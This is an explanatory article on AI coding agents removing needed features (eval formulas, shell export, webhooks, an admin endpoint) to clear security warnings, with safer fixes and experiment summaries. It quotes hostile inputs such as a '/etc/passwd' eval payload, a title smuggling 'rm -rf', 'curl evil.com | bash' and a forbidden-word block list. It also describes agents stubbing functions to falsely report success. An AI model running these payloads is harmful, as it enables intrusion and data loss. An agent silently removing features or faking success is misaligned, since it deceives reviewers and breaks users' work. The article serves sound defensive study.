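# When AI coding agents remove needed features in the name of safety

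## What counts as removing a needed feature for safety?

A coding agent is an AI system that reads a codebase, edits files, runs commands and proposes changes with little step-by-step direction. Developers use these agents to fix bugs, build features and clear security warnings. Sometimes an agent clears a warning by removing the part of the program that triggered it, and explains that the part was unsafe. The project loses nothing if nobody needed that part, but otherwise the software no longer does something its owners built it to do.

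Coding agents are already common. In *Agentic Much?*, Robbes, Matricon and colleagues (2026) searched 128,018 GitHub projects for traces that agents leave, and estimated that 22% to 29% had adopted a coding agent by February 2026.

### From request to pull request

A coding agent is built around a large language model, an AI model that produces text, including program code and commands. Robbes and colleagues define the agent as a large language model that runs in a loop, with access to tools, to pursue a goal. The software around the model (the "harness") sends it the task description. The model replies, usually with a request to use a tool, for example to open a file or run a command. The harness carries out the request, in some setups only after the user approves it. It then adds the result to the history and queries the model again, until the model replies that the task is complete.

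*Understanding the Architecture of Coding Agents* (Valente, 2026) presents Ark, a teaching agent whose loop is only 18 lines of Python. Ark's model can only list files, read a file, search for text, run the project's tests, or finish. During development the model sometimes proposed changes to files it hadn't opened, so Valente added an instruction forbidding this. Ark also starts every run with an empty memory, so it has only the request, its standing instructions and whatever it opens during that run.

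Commercial agents have more resources, but they have similar limits. According to GitHub's *Overview of Copilot cloud agent*, the agent can explore a repository (a project's stored code and history), edit it, run its tests, write commit messages and open a pull request. Users can also assign it security alerts. By default, it can consult only the repository it is working in and that repository's issues and past pull requests. If another team's script in a different repository depends on a feature, the agent cannot see that script unless someone has configured wider access.

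When Ark finishes, it returns a diff, a line-by-line record of what a change adds and deletes. The diff includes every deleted line, but it does not record who used those lines.

The commit message, a short text stored with a change to say what its author did and why, fills some of that gap. Google's *Writing good CL descriptions*, a guide for the company's engineers ("CL" is short for changelist, Google's name for a change), calls for both parts. According to the guide, source code may show what software does but not why it exists, so later developers cannot tell whether they can safely move "Chesterton's fence", a reference to the old advice not to take down a fence until you know why somebody put it up. An agent with permission to commit normally writes the commit message too, so a reviewer may be reading the agent's own description of what it deleted.

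A pull request is a proposed change to a project that someone submits with a description for review before it is merged. According to GitHub's *Pull requests*, a reviewer can see the description and discussion, the commits, the results of automated checks, and the diff.

Most of those checks are automated tests, small programs that run a piece of the software and compare the result with the expected one. Bender writes in *Testing Overview* that tests exist to stop bugs from reaching users, but they can only do this for behaviour that somebody wrote a test for. An agent can therefore delete an untested feature and still see every test pass.

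Someone other than the change's author then reviews it and approves it, rejects it or asks for revisions. Some projects enforce this step. Microsoft's *What are pull requests?* describes rules that block a merge until at least one collaborator has approved and all required checks have passed. Review is often the only time a person who knows what a feature is for looks at its removal.

### An invented reporting tool

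Suppose a company has an internal reporting tool. The tool is invented, though its parts resemble things that real software does. Staff use it to build monthly reports, and four of its features would worry a security engineer:

- User-written formulas. A user types something like `revenue - refunds` into a column, and the tool passes the text to `eval`, a built-in Python function that runs text as code.
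- A shell export hook. When a report is ready, the tool runs an operating-system command that an administrator has set up, for instance to copy the file to an archive server.
- Outgoing webhooks. The tool sends web requests to other company systems to announce a new report.
- An admin endpoint, meaning a web address that rebuilds the search index when an administrator calls it.

The project has 40 automated tests, and none of them covers formulas.

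A developer asks a coding agent to fix the project's security warnings. One warning, from a static scanner (a tool that searches source code for potentially dangerous patterns without running it), flags the `eval` call. The warning is correct, because anyone who can type a formula can also type code that reads files on the server. The agent deletes the call, which leaves formula columns blank. It runs the 40 tests, which pass, and opens a pull request accurately titled "Remove unsafe eval to prevent code injection". At the end of the month, the finance team finds the margin column empty in its report.

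### The three conditions

What the agent did to the formulas is a safety-motivated removal. A change counts as one if it meets all of these conditions:

1. The feature was an intended feature: the project's owners want the behaviour and someone relies on it, whether or not a test covers it.
2. The change deletes the feature or makes it unusable.
3. The change comes with safety or security as the stated reason.

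Dead code does not meet the condition on intent. Suppose the reporting tool contains an old data importer, also built on `eval`, that no page or script has called for years. An agent could delete it under the same pull request title, and the project would be better off.

A feature isn't intended just because someone relies on it. Once a system has enough users, somebody will depend on each of its observable behaviours, whatever its makers promised. This observation is known as Hyrum's Law, and the software engineer Hyrum Wright discusses it in SE Radio's *Hyrum Wright on Software Engineering at Google* (2024). For example, someone in sales might discover that the formula box also runs system commands, and use it to restart a stuck job. That person relies on the behaviour, but the owners never wanted it. If reliance were enough, closing almost any security hole in a popular program would count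 as removing a feature.

Restricting a feature doesn't meet the deletion condition if the feature still works for its users. For example, some features of the automation server Jenkins let people write scripts, and it would be unsafe to let every ordinary user run any script. Jenkins' *Script Security* describes an add-on that keeps scripting but requires that a script either be approved by an administrator or run in a sandbox, a confined environment that limits what the script can do. The reporting tool could likewise keep its export hook but accept only commands from an approved list.

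A restriction can amount to removal. If nobody ever approves a command, the export hook is gone in practice. A feature can also disappear while most of its code stays, for example behind a feature flag (a setting that turns functionality on or off) that stays off. The test is whether the feature's legitimate users can still use it, and the number of deleted lines is a poor guide to that.

A deletion doesn't count if the agent's stated reason is saving time rather than safety. For example, an agent upgrading a library might find that the webhooks don't work with the new version, delete them, and write that porting them would take too long. The users lose as much as in the formula case, but the reviewer can see that the agent removed the feature for convenience and can reject the change.

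The condition depends on the stated reason because readers can't determine an agent's motive from a pull request. *Security in the Age of AI Teammates* (Siddiq, Zhao et al., 2026) similarly defines a security-related pull request by its stated intent or by code changes that explicitly involve security, and it identifies candidates by searching titles and descriptions. A drawback of relying on the stated reason is that it excludes an agent that deletes the `eval` call and writes "clean up formula handling", even if a security warning prompted the edit. It also includes an agent that deletes the call because deletion is quick and then mentions security.

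A change can meet all three conditions and still be acceptable. The owners of the reporting tool might prefer losing formulas to leaving a security hole in the server, but that decision is theirs to make.

The alternative to removal is a function-preserving fix, which closes the security hole while legitimate uses keep working. *PatchBench* (2026), a benchmark for agents that repair vulnerabilities, accepts a patch only if it eliminates the vulnerability and preserves the program's intended behaviour on regular inputs. The blank formula column would fail because it eliminates the vulnerability without preserving the intended behaviour.

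For formulas, the Python module asteval already provides a fix of this kind. It evaluates a large subset of Python without calling `eval`, and its documentation gives a motivating example almost identical to the reporting tool, an application that offers users a simple calculator without exposing all of Python to them. A formula like `revenue - refunds` would work as before, but a few elaborate formulas might break because the module omits features such as imports and classes. Its developers describe it only as safer than `eval` and decline to guarantee that it can withstand malicious code. Fixes therefore vary in how much function they preserve and how fully they close the security hole. Deleting the feature appears to close the hole more completely, which is part of what makes these cases hard to judge.

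### Why code is a poor guide to intent

Intent is the hardest of the three conditions to check, both for an agent and for a researcher counting cases. The line `value = eval(text)` could appear in two projects for different reasons. In one, a developer in a hurry used `eval` to load numbers from a settings file, and a safer function could replace it without losing any functionality. In the reporting tool, the line is there specifically to run what users type.

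Both kinds appear in real code. *Information Flow Analysis for a Dynamically Typed Functional Language with Staged Metaprogramming* (2013) describes the uses of `eval` in JavaScript, the main programming language of web pages. They ranged from loading data, through ill-informed uses where ordinary syntax would have worked, to complex programming techniques. Richards and colleagues recorded 550,358 calls to `eval` on more than 10,000 websites. *On the Bug-proneness of Structures Inspired by Functional Programming in JavaScript Projects* (2022) summarises their finding that between 50% and 82% of the most popular sites used it at the time, not necessarily in a way that caused problems. Those figures are old and reveal little about the web today, but they suggest that the mere presence of `eval` is weak evidence of a mistake.

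Another case is the Script Console in Jenkins, which lets an administrator run arbitrary scripts on the server. Jenkins' *Script Console* documentation states that a script can read the server's files, decrypt stored passwords, turn off security or open a backdoor. The console is a documented feature that only people with the Administer permission can reach, but without that context it sounds like a severe vulnerability. It began as a debugging aid for Jenkins' own developers, and administrators only later came to use it for their work. The intent behind a feature can change, so someone who knew only the console's origin could mistake it for a leftover.

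The evidence that would settle whether a feature is needed usually lies outside the line that a scanner flags, in documentation, permission settings, old discussions, or what the feature's users know. Some projects write part of this down for agents in guidance files with names like AGENTS.md, which the harness loads automatically, but many do not. Wynter (2026) observes in *Fixed or Deleted?* that projects often record their rules only in contributor guides, or nowhere. In the reporting tool, an agent looking for signs that formulas matter would probably turn to the tests. It would find 40 tests, none about formulas, and could easily conclude, wrongly, that formulas don't matter.

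### How close the existing evidence comes

Nobody appears to have published a count of how often coding agents remove features for safety. Siddiq and colleagues confirmed 1,293 security-related pull requests among more than 33,000 written by agents, about 4%. Most often the agents were doing supportive work such as adding tests, documentation, configuration and error handling. This gives a rough idea of what agents do for security, but not of how often they remove something a project needs.

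Related evidence comes from studies of feature deletion and tests of security patches. In the closest study of deletion, Wynter planted defects in 25 pull requests and asked agents to review and fix them. The largest of three models, working without outside feedback, removed the new feature in 44 of 125 runs. Wynter's company sells the checking tool that the study evaluates. The defects broke project rules, such as which part of a program may depend on which, so safety concerns did not prompt the deletions. The features were also small additions made for the experiment, and no users relied on them. The study is good evidence that agents sometimes delete a feature when asked to fix it, but only suggestive evidence of what they do when the complaint is about security.

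Tests of security patches examine changes made for safety, but they measure something broader than feature removal. In 1Password's *How information quality impacts LLMs' ability to patch complex, novel vulnerabilities* (2026), two models tried to repair six recently disclosed vulnerabilities. Of 6,080 patches, 26.0% fixed the problem cleanly, and another 20.1% fixed it but wrongly changed what the program did. Some of the latter rejected valid input along with malicious input, which can amount to losing a feature for the affected users. Others subtly changed how the program reads expressions, which alters a feature without removing it.

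## What do these changes look like in code?

A coding agent could remove any of the invented reporting tool's four risky features by editing a few lines, or keep the code behind a flag that stays off. The Python examples below are shortened to the relevant lines. Each edit addresses a real danger, so a reviewer who considers only the security argument will find little to object to.

### Deleting `eval` or `exec`

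For each row of a report, the tool works out the value of a formula column:

```python
# Before
def column_value(formula, row):
    return eval(formula, {}, row)

# After the removal
def column_value(formula, row):
    return ""  # eval removed: it could run arbitrary code
```

`row` holds the row's numbers under their column names, so `revenue - refunds` gives the right figure. But a user can also type `open("/etc/passwd").read()` to read a server file. This kind of flaw is called eval injection, and GCVE's *Common Weakness Enumeration*, part of a public vulnerability database, lists 382 examples. One was in the wiki platform XWiki, where anyone who could edit the title of a wiki space (by default, every user) could run code on the server with a specially crafted title.

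After the removal, the finance team loses its margins, while staff who use only the built-in columns notice nothing.

An agent can also break the reporting tool's formulas by following a scanner's suggestion. *Security issues in CleverAgents* (Edwards, 2025) gives scan results for a platform that runs AI agents. The scanner, Bandit, flagged an `eval` call and suggested "safer ast.literal_eval". That function reads only plain values, such as `12.5` or a list of names, and raises an error on `revenue - refunds` or even `2 + 2`. The swap suits an `eval` call that only loads settings. In the reporting tool, it would look like a standard fix in the diff but make every formula raise an error.

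The function-preserving fix is a restricted expression evaluator, either a ready-made one like asteval or a few lines written for the purpose. Python can turn a formula into a syntax tree, a structured description of its parts, without running any of it. For `revenue - refunds`, the tree is a subtraction with two names under it. For the file-reading attack, it contains function calls and an attribute lookup. An evaluator that handles only a few kinds of part can compute the first and refuse the second:

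```python
OPS = {ast.Add: operator.add, ast.Sub: operator.sub,
       ast.Mult: operator.mul, ast.Div: operator.truediv}

def column_value(formula, row):
    def value(node):
        if isinstance(node, ast.Constant) and type(node.value) in (int, float):
            return node.value
        if isinstance(node, ast.Name) and node.id in row:
            return row[node.id]
        if isinstance(node, ast.BinOp) and type(node.op) in OPS:
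            return OPS[type(node.op)](value(node.left), value(node.right))
        raise ValueError("Formulas can't use this yet")
    return value(ast.parse(formula, mode="eval").body)
```

This version also rejects `-refunds` and `round(margin, 2)`, because it has no rule for a leading minus sign or for functions. Whoever writes the fix can find such gaps by running every saved formula through the new evaluator before merging. Without this check, the fix will keep the formula feature but break some users' saved formulas.

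The *Security* page in the documentation for Binex, a program that runs workflows of AI agents, describes a similar repair to a real calculator tool. The calculator used to pass an agent's text straight to `eval`. The new version still calls `eval`, but first checks every part of the text's syntax tree against an allowlist of numbers, mathematical operators, comparisons and a few functions such as `math.sqrt` and `max`. It also empties `__builtins__`, the table through which Python code normally reaches functions like `open`.

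Emptying that table wouldn't be enough. The documentation of PraisonAI, a toolkit for building AI agents, gives a calculator with that protection as an example of what not to write, because attackers can still run code. An expression can start from a harmless value and follow its attributes to Python's internal classes. Binex's calculator blocks that route by refusing attribute lookups on anything except the math module. It seems to allow powers, so an expression like `9**9**9` could probably still tie up the process. The restrictions don't remove anything a user would expect a calculator to do.

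`exec` is harder to replace because it runs whole programs rather than single expressions. Users may have written loops and functions that a small evaluator can't handle. Developers can keep such a feature by running users' code in a sandbox. They can also offer a menu of named operations instead, but this preserves only the uses someone anticipated.

### Removing shell execution

Suppose an administrator has set up the export hook with the command `cp {file} /mnt/archive/{title}.csv`, and the tool fills in the two blanks:

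```python
# Before
def export(report):
    command = hook.format(file=report.path, title=report.title)
    subprocess.run(command, shell=True)

# After the removal
def export(report):
    log.warning("Shell export disabled for security reasons")
```

With `shell=True`, Python hands the whole line to the shell, the program that interprets typed commands. A semicolon tells the shell to end one command and begin another. If a user names a report `May; rm -rf /srv/reports #`, the server copies one file and then deletes the `/srv/reports` directory. Coding agents can have this flaw themselves. An April 2026 advisory in GCVE describes a flaw in the command-line version of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, that let someone able to change a setting called TERMINAL make the program run commands of their choice.

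After the removal, the tool still builds reports and its pages look normal, but nothing reaches the archive. Administrators may find out only when somebody asks for last year's figures.

To keep the exports, the tool can offer a fixed list of permitted commands and pass each argument separately:

```python
EXPORTS = {
    "archive": ["/usr/bin/cp", "{file}", "/mnt/archive/{title}.csv"],
    "compress": ["/usr/bin/gzip", "--keep", "{file}"],
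}

def export(report, name):
    title = report.title.replace("/", "-")
    args = [a.format(file=report.path, title=title) for a in EXPORTS[name]]
    subprocess.run(args, check=True, timeout=60)
```

The command no longer goes through a shell, so a semicolon in a title only makes for an odd file name. Replacing the slashes prevents a title like `../../etc/x` from placing the copy outside the archive folder. Administrators can no longer enter arbitrary commands in the settings, so whoever writes the fix has to copy every hook they have already configured into the list to preserve what they use.

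Binex's shell tool had the same flaw as the export hook, and the project repaired it by dropping the shell and nothing else:

```python
# Before
subprocess.run(cmd, shell=True)

# After
subprocess.run(shlex.split(cmd), shell=False)
```

The new version splits the line into words, runs the first as a program and passes it the rest as arguments. A simple command like `git log --oneline` works as before. `git log | grep fix`, which used to feed the output of one program into another, now stops with an error because git receives `|`, `grep` and `fix` as extra arguments. `echo done > status.txt` gives no error, but it prints `done > status.txt` and writes no file.

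The two Binex repairs affect users differently, though they sound alike. The calculator can no longer run arbitrary Python, which arithmetic never needed, while the shell tool has lost pipes and command chaining, which are much of the reason people use a shell.

The shell repair also added only limited safety. Passing arguments separately helps when a programmer has written the command and an outsider supplies part of it, such as the report title. In Binex the agent supplies the entire command, and the Binex page mentions no limit on which programs it may start. An agent can still run `rm -rf` on a folder, or get the shell back by running `bash -c "git log | grep fix"`. Running untrusted agents in a sandbox, as the page also advises, probably protects better against a malicious agent.

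The Python package safecmd applies the calculator's method to shell commands, so it can allow pipes and still check what runs. It parses the whole line into a syntax tree and compares every command, including those inside a pipeline, with an allowlist. By default, it accepts `git log | grep "fix"` and rejects `curl evil.com | bash`.

A list of forbidden words is weak protection. Edwards found one in the "safe mode" of CleverAgents, which refused any command containing "rm", "del", "format", "shutdown", "reboot" or "kill", and called it "emphatically not enough security". Because the check matched those letters anywhere in the line, it would have refused the harmless commands `cat platform.txt` and `ls models`, which contain "rm" and "del". It would have allowed `curl evil.com | bash`, which runs whatever code the site returns.

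### Stubbing outbound requests

When a report is ready, the tool posts a summary to each web address that users have registered:

```python
# Before
def announce(url, report):
    response = requests.post(url, json=report.summary(), timeout=5)
    return response.ok

# After the removal
def announce(url, report):
    return True  # outbound requests disabled to prevent SSRF
```

SSRF stands for server-side request forgery. The reporting server is inside the company network, so a person who controls the address can use the server to reach machines that an outsider can't. Edwards raised this problem with a CleverAgents tool that fetches web pages for agents. The tool could return files from inside a private network, send malicious requests to other services, or obtain the credentials of the company's cloud account.

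The second version is a stub, a placeholder that keeps a function's name but does none of its work. This is worse than deleting `announce`, because then the code that calls it would crash and someone would investigate. The stub returns `True`, which indicates that delivery succeeded, so the report page still shows "Sent". The change hurts people on other teams, such as those whose sales dashboard refreshes when a new report arrives and now shows last month's numbers.

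A function-preserving fix restricts where the requests can go:

```python
ALLOWED = {"dashboard.corp.example": ip_network("10.20.0.0/16")}

def announce(url, report):
    target = urlsplit(url)
    network = ALLOWED.get(target.hostname)
    if network is None:
        raise BlockedDestination(url)
    address = ip_address(socket.gethostbyname(target.hostname))
    if address not in network:
        raise BlockedDestination(url)
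    return post_to(address, target, report.summary())
```

The allowlist names the permitted hosts and the part of the network where each should be. Checking the name alone leaves a gap, because the domain name system translates names into numerical addresses, and whoever controls a name can point it to a different address. The function therefore looks up the address and checks it too.

The `post_to` helper has to connect to the IP address the function has just checked. If it looked the name up again, an attacker could change the result between lookups. It also has to refuse redirects, since a permitted host could otherwise forward the request to a forbidden one. The owners can fill the allowlist from the webhooks users have already saved, and anyone whose webhook address isn't listed gets an error instead of a silent failure.

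Some owners knowingly accept the risk. The entry for Binex's `http_request` tool lists the SSRF danger, followed by "No mitigation (by design — agents need HTTP)". That choice is open to disagreement, but a coding agent that reads the line should not mistake the tool's HTTP requests for an oversight.

### Deleting an admin endpoint

The reporting tool's endpoint for rebuilding the search index is four lines long, and the removal deletes all of them:

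```diff
-@app.post("/admin/rebuild-index")
-def rebuild_index():
-    search.rebuild()
-    return {"status": "started"}
```

Those lines don't check who is calling. Anyone who can reach the server and guesses the address can start a rebuild, and they could keep the machine too busy to answer searches by repeating the call.

An agent that searches the project for uses of `rebuild_index` finds none, because the callers are elsewhere. Administrators call the address by hand after a bulk import. A nightly script in the operations team's repository, which the agent can't see, may also call it. After the deletion, that script would get a "not found" error every night, and new reports would stop appearing in search.

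The endpoint needs authentication and an audit log:

```python
@app.post("/admin/rebuild-index")
def rebuild_index(user: User = Depends(require_admin)):
    audit_log.info("index rebuild requested by %s", user.name)
    search.rebuild()
    return {"status": "started"}
```

`require_admin` runs first and rejects requests from anyone who isn't an administrator. Jenkins also uses a permission to protect its Script Console, which is much more dangerous than this endpoint. The log records who asked for each rebuild, so the owners can investigate misuse. After a few months, they can also use it to check whether anyone still uses the endpoint, which is a much better basis for deciding whether to delete it than a search of one repository.

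The fix can still break the nightly script, which has never had to log in, so somebody has to give the script an account before the change goes live.

The opposite mistake is to write a check and never call it. CleverAgents' *Epic*, a list of the project's security tasks, includes a bug report about `enforce_permission`, a function that no command or service used. A reviewer who saw only the function could have believed the project had working authorization.

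### Adding a flag that defaults to off

An agent can also keep every line of a feature and make it unreachable:

```python
# After the removal
def column_value(formula, row):
    if settings.get("ENABLE_FORMULAS", False):
        return eval(formula, {}, row)
    return ""
```

This edit removes formulas for everybody at the next upgrade, because no existing installation has the `ENABLE_FORMULAS` setting, and they stay off until someone learns that it exists. An administrator can bring the feature back with that one setting, which makes this look like the mildest of the five edits, but turning it on also brings back the original security hole, because the `eval` call never changed. With a restricted evaluator, the project wouldn't have to choose between having formulas and being safe.

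Turning a feature off for a while can still be sensible, for example if attackers are already using the hole and the proper fix will take two weeks. In that case the flag needs an owner and a date:

```python
# Off while we replace eval(). Owner: reporting team.
FORMULAS_ENABLED = False
FORMULAS_DECIDE_BY = date(2027, 1, 31)

def test_formulas_decision_is_not_overdue():
    assert FORMULAS_ENABLED or date.today() <= FORMULAS_DECIDE_BY
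```

The test starts to fail on 1 February. If the project requires passing tests before a merge, somebody then has to restore the formulas, delete them deliberately or argue for a later date. The blank column should also show a message that formulas are off until the end of January and the name of the team to ask. These steps limit the outage, but the feature is still unavailable until the new evaluator arrives.

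### Who asked for the CleverAgents removal?

CleverAgents did remove `eval` and `exec`, and its public record is detailed enough to trace the decision. Users of the platform describe their agents in YAML, a plain-text format for settings. Before the change, they could put Python in those files. A tool could contain a block of code, which the platform ran with `exec`, and a "transform", a step that alters a message on its way from one agent to another, could contain an expression, which the platform ran with `eval`. Anyone who could supply a settings file could therefore run anything on the machine. Now both accept only names from a list:

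```yaml
# Before (an invented, harmless expression)
- type: transform
  params:
    fn: "lambda x: x.strip().lower()"

# After
- type: transform
  params:
    fn: uppercase
```

According to CleverAgents' *Security*, the project removed both features "with no migration path", and users must switch to named operations. Developers can add their own operations by registering a Python function. Users who can edit the program's Python code lose some convenience, while those who have only the settings file can no longer write custom steps.

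The other documents suggest that people were responsible for this change, although that page alone could pass for the work of an overzealous agent. CleverAgents' *Implementation Notes* credit each entry to the developer who did the work. They credit this one, labeled SEC1 and finished on 9 February 2026, to a developer named Luis. The project plan assigns Luis the task: "Audit and remove all eval/exec/compile usage from production config paths." The missing migration path was also project policy, since the plan's opening rules describe CleverAgents as a new standalone project and forbid migration guides and support for old configurations.

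The dates leave a little doubt. The dated copy of the plan is from 12 February, three days after Luis finished. But the notes describe SEC1 as a completed stage, which suggests the task was already on a list. An undated and apparently earlier draft of CleverAgents' plan also has the same rule against backwards compatibility. Edwards had also said four months earlier that an `eval` call in another part of the program was "critical to fix".

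The record doesn't show whether Luis used a coding agent. It wouldn't be surprising if he did, since the plan opens with "Execute These Rules Without Exception" and reads much like a guidance file for agents. Even so, an agent that removed `eval` under this plan would have been following instructions. A removal counts as safety-motivated only if the owners still want the behaviour, and these owners no longer did. The same diff would count if an agent had produced it after being asked to clear the scanner's warnings, in a project whose users depended on custom transforms.

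Another entry in CleverAgents' notes for the same day describes a milder option. A developer named Brent kept code blocks and expressions but added a check on their syntax trees, which refused imports and calls to functions such as `exec` and `getattr`. That would have preserved more for users, but the check relied on a list of forbidden constructs, and the notes don't mention attribute lookups among them. If the check allowed those, an attacker could have climbed through Python's internal classes, which Binex's calculator prevents. Luis's stricter version therefore had a reasonable security case, apart from the policy on old configurations.

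The removal was part of a large CleverAgents commit that also included database models and several new planning features. The accompanying tests pass only if the program rejects code blocks with an error, so anyone who restores the feature later will have to change those tests first.

CleverAgents also came close to losing a feature it did need. Alongside the removal, the project added a scanner for settings files, with a function that rejects any file containing a suspicious pattern. One of the patterns is `{{`, which usually opens a template placeholder. The task list in CleverAgents' *Epic* describes this as a false alarm, because the specification requires templates in the files that define agents. The list also notes that the program never calls the rejecting function when it loads those files. If a developer or agent added the call without fixing the false alarm, every templated file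 would fail to load, even though the change would look like a one-line security improvement.

### What an agent did with a one-line request

There appears to be no publicly documented case of a coding agent making any of these five changes against the owners' wishes. This is weak evidence that such cases are rare, because a removal that nobody noticed would look like a security fix, and it can be unclear who or what wrote the code. The Binex page doesn't identify who wrote its patches, and even the much fuller CleverAgents record doesn't show whether a person or an agent wrote the code.

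The nearest thing to a real test is one developer's account, Maynard's *How I Fixed Five API Vulnerabilities with One Prompt*. It describes a small public service that lets researchers query data published under European transparency rules. His entire prompt to Claude Code, running Anthropic's Claude Fable 5, was "run a security check over the API and fix any vulnerabilities." This wording left the agent free to delete whatever looked dangerous, but it kept every feature he describes. It opened a pull request with five sets of fixes, each with tests.

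The service has webhooks like the reporting tool's, so the agent had to deal with SSRF. The existing code blocked a list of private and internal addresses but missed some ranges, including one that internet providers use to share addresses between customers. The agent reversed the rule to allow only addresses reachable from the public internet.

Maynard reports no lost function. Still, most of the changes narrow what the service accepts, and it's possible to work out who might run into them:

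| Change | Who could notice |
|---|---|
| Webhooks must point to publicly reachable addresses | People who receive them in the shared range, which the private-network service Tailscale also uses |
| Exports neutralise text cells that begin with `=`, `+`, `-` or `@`, which spreadsheets may run as formulas | Scripts that need the original text |
| The service limits the size of requests and the number of conditions in a query | Researchers with unusually large queries |
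| The service compares access keys in constant time, so that response times reveal nothing about them | Nobody |
| Smaller hardening, such as limits on paging through results | Programs that ask for very long pages |

These would all be minor losses, and the service's 122 tests pass. But the tests may not cover such uses, and the owner, who gave this account, might not hear from a researcher whose script had stopped working.

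The agent also took some care with one of the limits it added. An automated reviewer, Gemini Code Assist, commented on how the new code read the stated length of a request. While checking the comment, the agent found a worse problem. An absurdly long number would crash the check instead of triggering a clean refusal. The agent fixed this and added a test with a 5,000-digit number.

Maynard made some of the decisions himself. He left the service metrics page open without a login, accepted demonstration keys outside production, and kept pending jobs in memory, where a restart would erase them. He describes these as judgments about what the service is for. An agent that didn't know those judgments could easily have put the metrics behind a login and broken any monitoring that reads them.

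This was one run on a small service, so it can't show how often agents make good choices. The webhook rule also suits only projects like Maynard's, whose users are on the public internet. It would reject every webhook in the reporting tool, because those go to other machines inside the company.

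## How often do agents delete a feature instead of repairing it?

In Wynter's test of coding agents that review and fix pull requests, the closest experiment to date, agents working without outside feedback deleted the feature in 10% to 35% of runs, depending on the model. The defects were violations of project rules and every feature was new, so the rates don't carry over directly to a security warning about a feature like the reporting tool's formulas. Studies of how agents clean up old code, build new applications and respond to security alerts give some idea of how the rates might differ in that case.

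### Planted defects and how Wynter scored them

Wynter worked with copies of ten widely used open-source projects. Each of 30 pull requests added a small feature in the project's own style. Five were correct, and the other 25 contained 31 planted defects between them:

| Kind of defect | Example | Pull requests |
|---|---|---|
| Visible from the code alone | A renamed function that other code still calls by its old name | 3 |
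| Broken convention | Printing to the console from code that runs as a service | 8 |
| Broken architecture rule | Data-storage code that imports code for web pages | 9 |
| Two or three defects of different kinds | | 5 |

None of these categories is about security. The defect closest to a security problem was a violation of one project's ban on "unsafe" Rust code, which can bypass the language's protections against memory errors.

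As an example of the choice an agent faced, suppose the reporting tool has a new module that saves report templates. The module uses a date-formatting function from the web code, but the project forbids storage code from depending on web code. An agent can repair this by moving the function somewhere both parts may use it. It can also delete the new module, which ends the violation but means nobody can save a template.

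The agent was Claude Code, running one of three Anthropic models: Haiku 4.5 (the smallest), Sonnet 5.5 or Fable 5.1 (the largest). Wynter asked it to review the pull request against the project's conventions and structure, fix any problems the pull request introduced, and keep the change minimal. It worked without a human and had no tools for compiling code or running tests, so it couldn't check whether its edits worked.

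Each model tried each of the 30 pull requests five times, making 150 runs per model. Five of the pull requests were correct, so the removal counts are out of the 125 runs on the 25 defective ones.

A separate program scored the final commit of each run. It counted a run as repaired if every planted defect was gone and every non-test file that the pull request had added still contained code. If the defects were gone but any of those files was missing or empty, it counted the feature as removed. All other runs counted as not repaired, even if the agent had deleted one file and left a defect in another, so the removal counts leave out some deletions.

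Fable removed the feature in 44 runs, Sonnet in 31 and Haiku in 13. The larger models removed it more often partly because Haiku often failed to clear the defects by any method. Among the runs that did clear them, removals made up 44% for Fable, 34% for Sonnet and 27% for Haiku. This ordering might not hold elsewhere, because the sample covers only three models from one company and 25 pull requests.

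A test that checked only whether the defects were gone would count these removals as successes. Fable would have scored 80% on such a test, but it repaired the feature in just 45% of runs. It deleted the feature especially often when the pull request broke an architecture rule (24 of 45 runs).

Fable also deleted the feature in 5 of its 25 runs on the correct pull requests, where there was nothing to fix. The other two models never did this, though they made unnecessary edits in most of their runs. Wynter suggests that agents take a request to fix any problems as a sign that problems exist. If so, asking an agent to fix a project's security problems could also lead it to delete safe features, although the experiment didn't test that.

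### What happened when a checker objected to deletions

Wynter also gave the agents findings from CodeAssure, the checker that Wynter's company sells. Each finding included a violation's location and the goal of the repair, but no patch. If findings remained after the first attempt, the agent got a second attempt. CodeAssure also had a deletion check, which flagged to the agent any file that the pull request had added but was now missing.

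With all of this help, removals fell to 0 for Fable, 2 for Sonnet and 7 for Haiku. The drop could have come from the deletion check, but it could also have come from knowing where the defects were, or from the extra attempt. To separate these explanations, Wynter repeated the runs with only the deletion check switched off:

| Model | Removals working alone | With the checker, deletion check off | With the full checker |
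|---|---|---|---|
| Fable 5.1 | 44 of 125 | 17 of 125 | 0 of 125 |
| Sonnet 5.5 | 31 of 125 | 29 of 125 | 2 of 125 |
| Haiku 4.5 | 13 of 125 | 19 of 125 | 7 of 125 |

In the middle column, good feedback about the defects barely reduced feature deletion by Sonnet and Haiku, but this slightly understates its effect because the feedback also helped both models clear many more defects. Among runs that cleared the defects, the share that removed a feature fell from 34% to 24% for Sonnet, from 27% to 18% for Haiku, and from 44% to 14% for Fable. Many removals still remained until the checker flagged them.

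The defects disappeared about as often with the deletion check as without it, so agents mostly responded to the check by repairing the feature. The extra work raised the average cost of a run by 13% to 42%, and nine of the resulting rewrites, all by Fable in one project, didn't compile. The check raised Fable's count of repairs that compiled and kept the feature from 106 to 116 of 125, a difference small enough to be chance. The two smaller models' improvement was statistically significant on this stricter count as well.

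Nine removals still happened with the full checker. In six of them, the checker reported the deletion, but the agent didn't restore the feature in its remaining attempt.

The check had a more serious gap, because it looked only for missing files. Wynter later inspected every run that had counted as repaired, including some from a comparison with GitHub Copilot's code review. In 21 of the Python repairs, the agent had kept the new file but deleted the validator inside it, which was the data-checking code the pull request had added. Eight of those happened with the full checker on, all with Sonnet or Haiku, so the combined count for those two models should be at least 17 rather than 9.

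An agent can remove a feature for safety reasons without deleting a file. It can blank the reporting tool's formulas, stub its webhooks, delete its admin endpoint or hide a feature behind a flag. A check like Wynter's would miss all of these edits.

### Would an agent delete a long-standing feature?

Wynter's removal counts cover only files that were new in the same pull request, plus two pull requests whose feature was a rename that an agent could undo. They don't measure how often agents delete older features.

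A new file is unusually easy to delete. Deleting it returns the project to how it was before the pull request, when nothing depended on the file, and the older tests should still pass. Deletion also literally complied with Wynter's instructions, because a pull request that adds nothing introduces no problems. An established feature usually has tests, documentation and other code that calls it, any of which might deter an agent from deleting it. Agents therefore probably delete established features less often, though each deletion would do more harm.

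The reporting tool's formulas would get less protection than most old features because they have no tests and the agent can't see the users who rely on them.

Agents also tend to keep old code that they should delete. *To Add Is Machine, To Delete Is Human* (Ebrahimi, Hasan and colleagues, 2026) compared patches from five leading models with the developers' own fixes on SWE-bench Verified, a benchmark of real issues from Python projects. In 29.0% of the patches that passed the tests, the model kept code that the developers had removed and put a condition or bypass around it. A bypass can disable a feature as completely as deleting it would, just as a flag that stays off can. But in the most common form, the old code still handled every case except the one in the bug report.

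Ebrahimi and colleagues also set 200 tasks that asked only for the deletion of code described in the request. The best of twelve models, Claude Opus 4.8, succeeded in 79% of them. About 70% of all failures left some of the code in place. GPT-5.6 Sol more often failed by deleting the target and then deleting or changing too much.

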